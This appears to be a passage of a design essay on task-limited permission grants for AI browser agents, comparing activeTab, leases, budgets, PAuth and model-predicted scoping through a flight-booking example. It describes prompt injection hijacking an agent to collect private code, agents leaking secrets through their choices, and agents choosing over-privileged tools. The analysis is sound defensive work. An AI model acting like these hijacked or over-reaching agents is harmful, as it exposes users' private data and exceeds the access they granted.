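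Across 9,760 sessions with six models and no attacker, agents that held a secret revealed it through such choices 61.1% of the time. Some of these choices may have matched the secret by chance, so the researchers also ran sessions in which the agent knew no secret. Wang and colleagues found no leaks when agents visited two sites in turn without an attacker, but they checked only for private data that the agent had written out.

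SOPGuard checks the text an agent types, so it probably wouldn't detect a click on the union's registration link. SPIDES would probably allow the click too, because its rules let private data influence an action as long as no untrusted text has influenced the agent.

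## Designing a grant that lasts for one task

A task grant would give an agent access to the sites and actions that one stated task needs, and the access would end with the task. Chrome's origin sets and the plans that users approve in Claude's classic panel already do part of this.

`activeTab` is a useful pattern because its trigger, scope, powers and end are all clear. Each has an equivalent for tasks:

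| Part | `activeTab` | Task grant |
|---|---|---|
| Trigger | The user invokes the extension | The user states a task and submits it |
| Scope | The origin of the page in one tab | A set of sites |
| Powers | Whatever the extension can do to a page | The actions the task needs on each site |
| End | The tab moves to another origin or closes | The agent completes the task, the time runs out or the user cancels |

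A browser can enforce `activeTab` without knowing what the user wants, because it only has to recognise a click and compare origins. To enforce a task grant, a person or a model has to interpret the sentence describing the task and decide which sites the grant covers and when the task is finished.

### Starting and ending a task

When a user types and submits a task, the browser can at least verify that the user was there. Many agents also start work by themselves. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) describes OpenClaw and similar open-source agents, which run in a continuous loop and wait for events, such as a message from the user, a timer or a request from another program.

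For scheduled work, the user could approve the schedule once, and the browser could issue a new, short grant for each run. An agent that checks fares every Monday would then have access for a few minutes a week. But the approval would be a kind of standing access, since it would continue until someone withdrew it. If the agent needed another site, nobody would be there to approve it, so the agent would have to stop or wait. This arrangement is acceptable for checking fares but would be much riskier for a weekly purchase.

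The end of a task is also hard to define. The agents that Pirch and colleagues describe stop when the model signals that it has finished or when they reach a maximum number of steps. A model misled by a malicious page could keep working, and an agent can reach the step limit before the job is done. Some tasks have no natural end. An agent that rebooks a flight whenever the price falls might need access until the day of departure.

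A task grant needs a time limit that the agent can't extend. In *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning*, Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa (2026) propose leases, which are permissions that expire. In their example, an agent can hold read permission for up to 60 minutes and write permission for up to 20. The agent can give up either permission early, and a program it doesn't control withdraws each one when its time runs out. A request already on its way to a site when permission is withdrawn may still go through.

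### Choosing sites and actions

With `activeTab`, the user already has the right page open, but an agent's task may need dozens of sites that the user doesn't recognise. This is one reason to let a model choose the sites, as Chrome does.

The agent may also discover midway that it needs another site. The browser could ask the user each time. If it instead approved every new site automatically, a malicious page could widen the grant by linking to another site. One compromise would be to split the task, so that the agent first searches public pages without being logged in, then requests a second grant for the site the user chooses.

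Limiting actions is harder than limiting sites, because a browser can't reliably tell what a click will do. Websites could solve this by offering agents separate functions, such as one for searching for flights and another for booking them. Most research on task permissions assumes that such functions exist, so its results don't directly apply to agents that click through ordinary web pages.

Permissions that are reasonable on their own can also be dangerous together, as when an agent can read webmail and post on a public forum. In *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents*, Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues (2026) reviewed 89 sources and named limits on combined access as one of two main unsolved problems.

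The elastic proposal has a fixed rule that an agent may not combine untrusted input, sensitive data, and a way to send data out or change something outside within one session. The rule still applies after access to the sensitive data expires, because the agent may remember what it read. This is sensible, but it blocks some legitimate work, such as moving private code to a public project, unless the owner approves an exception.

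### Passing a task to other agents

An agent may give parts of a task to other agents, called sub-agents. One might compare fares while another handles the calendar. `activeTab` offers no model for this, because its grant belongs to one extension in one tab. Surapani and colleagues warn that sub-agents may have their own memories and credentials, so their authority can drift from what the user delegated.

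Under a simple rule, a sub-agent could receive only part of its parent's grant and would lose it when the parent loses its own. The elastic proposal adds that all the agents working for one parent share its limits, so that an agent can't get around a limit by creating more sub-agents. This is harder to apply when the sub-agent belongs to another company, and Parkinson and colleagues leave that as an open question.

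### Booking a flight under four kinds of access

Suppose a user asks an agent to find the cheapest direct flight to Lisbon on 12 May, book it if it costs no more than $300, and add it to their calendar. The agent searches the sites of three airlines, North, South and West, and finds that South has the cheapest one.

Assume that each search takes two pages, the booking three more and the calendar one, for a total of ten. The agent keeps each site in its own tab. The table leaves out the payment prompt because the user confirms the payment under every kind of access.

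| Kind of access | Prompts during the task | Access left afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| Standing access to all sites | 0 | Every site |
| Approval for each site, kept until revoked | 4 | The three airlines and the calendar |
| A grant for each page | 10 | None |
| A task grant | 1 | None |

Because Chrome's `activeTab` covers an origin instead of a single page, the user would click only four times, once in each tab. In a single tab, the user would need five clicks, because the agent would have to return to South after visiting West. However, an extension would keep its access in any tab the user left open on one of these sites.

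The task grant requires the fewest prompts of the three narrower options, but its prompt takes more effort to read. It might contain something like this, which is an illustration and not an existing format:

```
search:  north.example, south.example, west.example
book:    one ticket, at the lowest fare found, up to $300
add:     one event on calendar.example
end:     when the event is saved, after 20 minutes,
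         or when the user cancels
```

If the browser could enforce only the list of sites, the agent could also book on all three airlines and read every appointment in the calendar. A read-only set wouldn't work for the airlines, because searching for a fare usually involves filling in a form.

If South used a separate site for payment, approving each site would take five prompts. The task grant would take two unless the plan already included the payment site. There would still be ten page grants, since the payment page is already counted.

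Even this ordinary task would probably break the elastic proposal's rule about combinations. The airline pages are untrusted input, the calendar is private, and booking a ticket changes external state. The user would have to approve an exception, or the calendar would have to let the agent add an event without reading existing ones.

When a task grant ends, South still has the passenger's details and the agent may still have the fares and the itinerary in its history.

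### Measuring exposure in site-hours

One way to compare these designs is to multiply the number of sites an agent can access by the hours for which it can access them. This calculation covers 30 days:

```
standing access:  100 sites × 24 hours × 30 days       = 72,000 site-hours
activeTab:        10 uses a day × 3 minutes × 30 days  =     15 site-hours
task grants:      30 tasks × 20 minutes × 4 sites      =     40 site-hours
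```

The numbers are illustrative and rest on three assumptions: every site counts equally, each `activeTab` use covers one site and ends after three minutes, and each task grant covers all four sites for the full 20 minutes. The two cases also involve different amounts of work, because the user invokes the extension 300 times but gives the agent only 30 tasks.

The gap between standing access and the other two stays large under most changes to these assumptions. If the browser is open for only eight hours a day, standing access falls to 24,000 site-hours, still 600 times the figure for task grants.

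The figures for temporary access depend on the grants ending. If a user invokes an extension on their webmail each morning and leaves the tab open for eight hours, that adds 240 site-hours a month. A single four-site task grant that never ended would add 2,880 site-hours a month, 72 times the 40 site-hours for all 30 tasks. If the browser opened each site only for the five minutes when the agent needed it, the total for the 30 tasks would fall from 40 site-hours to 10.

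Site-hours don't account for the value of each site, so an hour of access to a weather forecast counts as much as an hour of access to a bank. They also don't account for what the agent can do there, although booking a flight is riskier than reading a fare. Researchers have tried to correct for this with weights. In the elastic proposal, the suggested weights are 1 for reading, 3 for writing and 9 for changing settings or other people's access, though Parkinson and colleagues acknowledge that the exact values are arbitrary.

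The measure also doesn't capture how much harm an agent could do during the permitted time. An agent can leak a document in seconds, so cutting a grant from 20 minutes to 10 may not reduce the damage at all. For this reason, Parkinson and colleagues recommend that irreversible actions require approval each time or be impossible for the agent.

The risk of leaving access open between tasks depends on the attack. An attacker who takes over an extension, as happened with Cyberhaven's, can use its standing access at any time. Prompt injection works only while the agent is reading the attacker's text, and a task grant would also be open then. Task grants therefore protect against prompt injection mainly by limiting which sites the agent can access, and much less by expiring sooner.

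### Checking each action against the user's words

Most online services use OAuth, a standard that lets other programs act for a user without the user's password. A bank using OAuth can give an agent permission to make transfers, but the permission normally covers any amount and any recipient. In *Beyond OAuth*, Sharma, Jiang and colleagues (2026) propose PAuth, a system in which the user's task replaces this permission. They compare the task to the buttons designed by Roesner and colleagues, where the user's own action authorises one specific use.

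Suppose the task is to pay a quarter of the user's Citi credit card balance from their Chase account if the balance is over $1,000. PAuth works like this:

1. The user signs the text of the task, and the agent sends it to both banks.
2. A language model on Chase's server translates the task into a short program. Ordinary code then extracts the part that determines the transfer, which the researchers call a natural-language slice.
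3. The agent asks Citi for the balance. Citi returns $1,200 with a signature and a record of the request that produced it.
4. The agent asks Chase to transfer $300 and attaches Citi's signed answer.
5. Chase checks the signature, confirms that $1,200 is over $1,000, and calculates that a quarter of it is $300. Since the amount and recipient match, it makes the transfer.

If the agent asks for $301 or names another recipient, Chase asks the user. A prompt injection can't change the rule, because Chase's model reads only the task and a description of the available functions.

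Sharma and colleagues tested this with 100 tasks in banking, messaging, travel, office work and shopping. They also wrote 634 requests that departed from the tasks, for example by changing an amount or skipping a condition. PAuth caught all 634. With the original wording, it allowed 71 of the 100 tasks without a prompt. The other 29 were too vague or told the agent to find instructions elsewhere, such as in a file. When the wording was complete, PAuth allowed all 100 without a prompt.

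These are strong results for tasks with precise wording. The researchers acknowledge that their benchmark is favourable, and they also assume that users review each task carefully. A harmful action that fits the task would still pass. If the user mistyped the recipient's account number, Chase would send the money to the wrong account.

For the flight, South's server would have to check something like this:

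```
allow South.book(fare) if
  fare = min(North's fare, South's fare, West's fare)
  and fare ≤ $300
```

All three airlines would need to support PAuth and sign their fares, or the user would need a trusted intermediary. The airlines would also receive the text of the task, so South could learn that the user was willing to pay $300 before it quoted a price. Sharma and colleagues consider this disclosure unavoidable, because a server needs the text to check an action against the task.

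### Predicting permissions from a task

Noyan (2026), in *Empirical Evaluation of Task-Based Permission Scoping Architecture for AI Agents*, uses a model to predict which permissions a task needs before the agent starts. The agent never receives the others. The system grants a permission only if three checks agree:

- The employee's department is allowed to have it.
- A model predicts from the task's description that the task needs it.
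- It doesn't form a forbidden combination with another permission, such as reading a database and sending requests to outside websites.

Noyan tested this with written tasks from an imaginary company. He weighted 15 permissions from 1 to 3 by risk, and an agent with all of them scored 31 points. The department limits alone reduced this exposure by 27.9%, and adding the model raised the reduction to 84.4%.

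That figure overstates how well the system works, because it also counts permissions that the agent needed. The system withheld at least one needed permission in 23 of the 100 test tasks. Noyan had decided in advance that the model should do this in fewer than 10% of tasks and reach a precision of at least 0.90, but no setting he tried met both conditions.

The model was a small one that Noyan had trained for the job. He compared it with Claude Haiku 4.5, a general-purpose model from Anthropic, using the same thresholds:

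| | Noyan's model | Claude Haiku 4.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Tasks that lost a needed permission | 21% | 11% |
| Tasks that received an unneeded permission | 23% | 42% |

Neither model is clearly better, because a missing permission interrupts the user and an unneeded one gives an attacker more to use. Noyan prefers the stricter model for security but acknowledges that Haiku may suit companies that can't tolerate interruptions.

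Part of the problem was that the permissions were too broad. One permission, `database_read`, accounted for 34% of the remaining unneeded exposure after weighting, because it covered both harmless and sensitive records. A permission for a whole website has the same weakness.

### Limiting access with a budget

In Parkinson and colleagues' elastic proposal, the agent begins with a few permissions and requests more as it works, so not everything has to be predicted at the start. The agent's owner sets an outer limit on these permissions. Each extra permission uses up a budget for as long as the agent holds it. A permission uses more of the budget when it is more powerful, when the agent makes repeated requests, and when the agent gets closer to a forbidden combination. When the budget runs out, the agent loses all its extra permissions.

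One example is a simulated coding agent with a budget of 600 units, which refills at five units a minute. To fix a program, the agent first requests permission to read the code, then permission to change it, and gives up both when it has finished. This uses 93 units, whereas requesting both permissions at the start, each lasting 20 minutes, would have used 240.

In another simulated task, a prompt injection makes the agent collect the user's private code. It gains access to eight private projects before the budget stops it. The rule about combinations, not the budget, keeps it from publishing the code.

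The budget puts an upper limit on exposure. Apart from any extra that the owner approves, the agent can't use more than it had at the start plus what the budget gains over time:

```
maximum in one hour = 600 + 5 × 60 = 900 units
```

Reading one project uses at least one unit a minute, so even a hijacked agent could read at most 15 projects for the whole hour. That access could still be enough to steal all their contents.

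The paper has no experimental results, and Parkinson and colleagues chose the numbers to illustrate the idea. The main question they leave open is whether agents would use such a budget sensibly.

### How often agents choose more access than they need

An agent could in principle limit itself by choosing the least powerful tool that works. As evidence that agents often don't, the elastic proposal cites *When Lower Privileges Suffice* (Yang, Bu and colleagues, 2026), which found that 6 of 11 agents chose an over-privileged tool in more than 30% of cases across 544 scenarios.

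The researchers gave each simulated scenario six tools, any of which could complete the task. Three needed few privileges, and the other three had more power than necessary, for example because they bypassed an approval step. The researchers counted a scenario against an agent if the agent used a powerful tool before trying all three safer ones.

The summary in the elastic proposal omits that the safer tools failed temporarily the first time the agent called them. The 30% figure therefore mostly measures how agents respond to errors. GPT-5.2, for example, chose a powerful tool immediately in only five scenarios, but chose one in 35 after two safer tools had failed. GPT-5.2, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GLM-5 all stayed below 10% overall.

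In *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?*, Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026) ran the same scenarios on eight models, seven of which Yang and colleagues had also tested. Three of the eight used a powerful tool in more than 30% of scenarios. When the safer tools worked the first time, the rates for two of those three were only 8.1% and 6.1%. The researchers didn't run this check on the third.

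Some results changed a lot between the studies. Llama 3.1 8B fell from 55.9% to 12.9%, partly because it often called tools that didn't exist. The exact percentages are therefore less reliable than the general pattern. Neither study tested the newest models. The rerun included Claude Sonnet 4.6, although Claude Sonnet 5.5 was already available.

The measure may also understate the problem. An agent didn't count as over-privileged if it tried each safer tool once and then used a powerful one, even though a safer tool always worked on the second call. Kimi K2.5's official rate was 18.0%, but it used a powerful tool at some point in 87.3% of scenarios.

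In the rerun, most models also waited longer before using a powerful tool when the descriptions labeled how powerful each tool was. Labels worked better when combined with an instruction to use the least privilege. With both, the share of scenarios that Qwen3.5-397B completed without a powerful tool rose from 18.8% to 51.1%. These changes are easy to make, but the model still failed to do this in almost half of the scenarios, so the browser still has to enforce the limit.

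If South's search page failed to load, an agent with access to every site might look for fares in the user's webmail instead. An agent with a task grant would have to try again, choose another airline or ask the user.

### Who should set the scope

The proposals disagree about who should turn a task into permissions:

| Who sets the scope | Likely errors | Burden |
|---|---|---|
| The user | Approving too much, or describing the task too vaguely | Reading plans and answering prompts |
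| A model | Leaving out a site the task needs, or adding one it doesn't | Correcting the model when it leaves something out |
| A fixed policy | Allowing far more than one task needs, or blocking unusual tasks | Writing the rules and keeping them up to date |

The argument for relying on the user is that only they know what they meant, but they can't review everything an agent does. Of the 100 tasks in Sharma and colleagues' benchmark, 44 needed at least three actions and 26 needed at least five. Some of those actions involve values the user has never seen, such as an amount the agent calculated during the task.

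In the elastic proposal, Parkinson and colleagues cite a report from Anthropic that users of its coding agent approved 93% of permission prompts. This suggests that prompts rarely stop an action, though it doesn't prove that users approved carelessly, since most of the requests may have been fine. Asking once about the whole task gives people a better chance to notice a mistake, provided the plan is short.

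A model reduces this burden but makes mistakes that the user has to correct. If Noyan's 21% rate of missing permissions also applied to browser tasks, someone who gave an agent 30 tasks a month would have to step in about six times. An attacker who can change the task's description can mislead the model into granting too much. Chrome reduces a similar risk by not showing web pages to the model that approves sites.

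Fixed policies can't be misled by a web page, but they don't adapt to the task. In Noyan's tests, the rules against dangerous combinations of permissions added no measurable protection while the model was working. Without the model, they cut exposure in three departments by 11.5% to 13.6% but blocked 6% to 31% of those departments' legitimate tasks. Nearly all of the blocked tasks needed only one of the two permissions in the forbidden pair. Noyan expects fewer problems if the system checks the rules when an agent tries to use the second permission, but didn't test this.

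Sharma and colleagues also argue that a fixed limit can't replace the user's instructions. If a company lets its agents spend up to $500 and a user tells an agent to pay $100, that agent shouldn't be able to pay $499. They're right, but a limit can still contain the damage when the user's wording is vague or a model misinterprets it.

The best arrangement is probably to give a fixed policy, the model and the user the decisions each handles well. When the task is booking a flight, a fixed policy could keep the agent away from the user's bank and webmail, and the model could propose three airline sites. The user would set the date and price limit and approve the sites. They would easily notice an unexpected site in the plan, but they might never find out that the model had left out a fourth airline with a cheaper flight.
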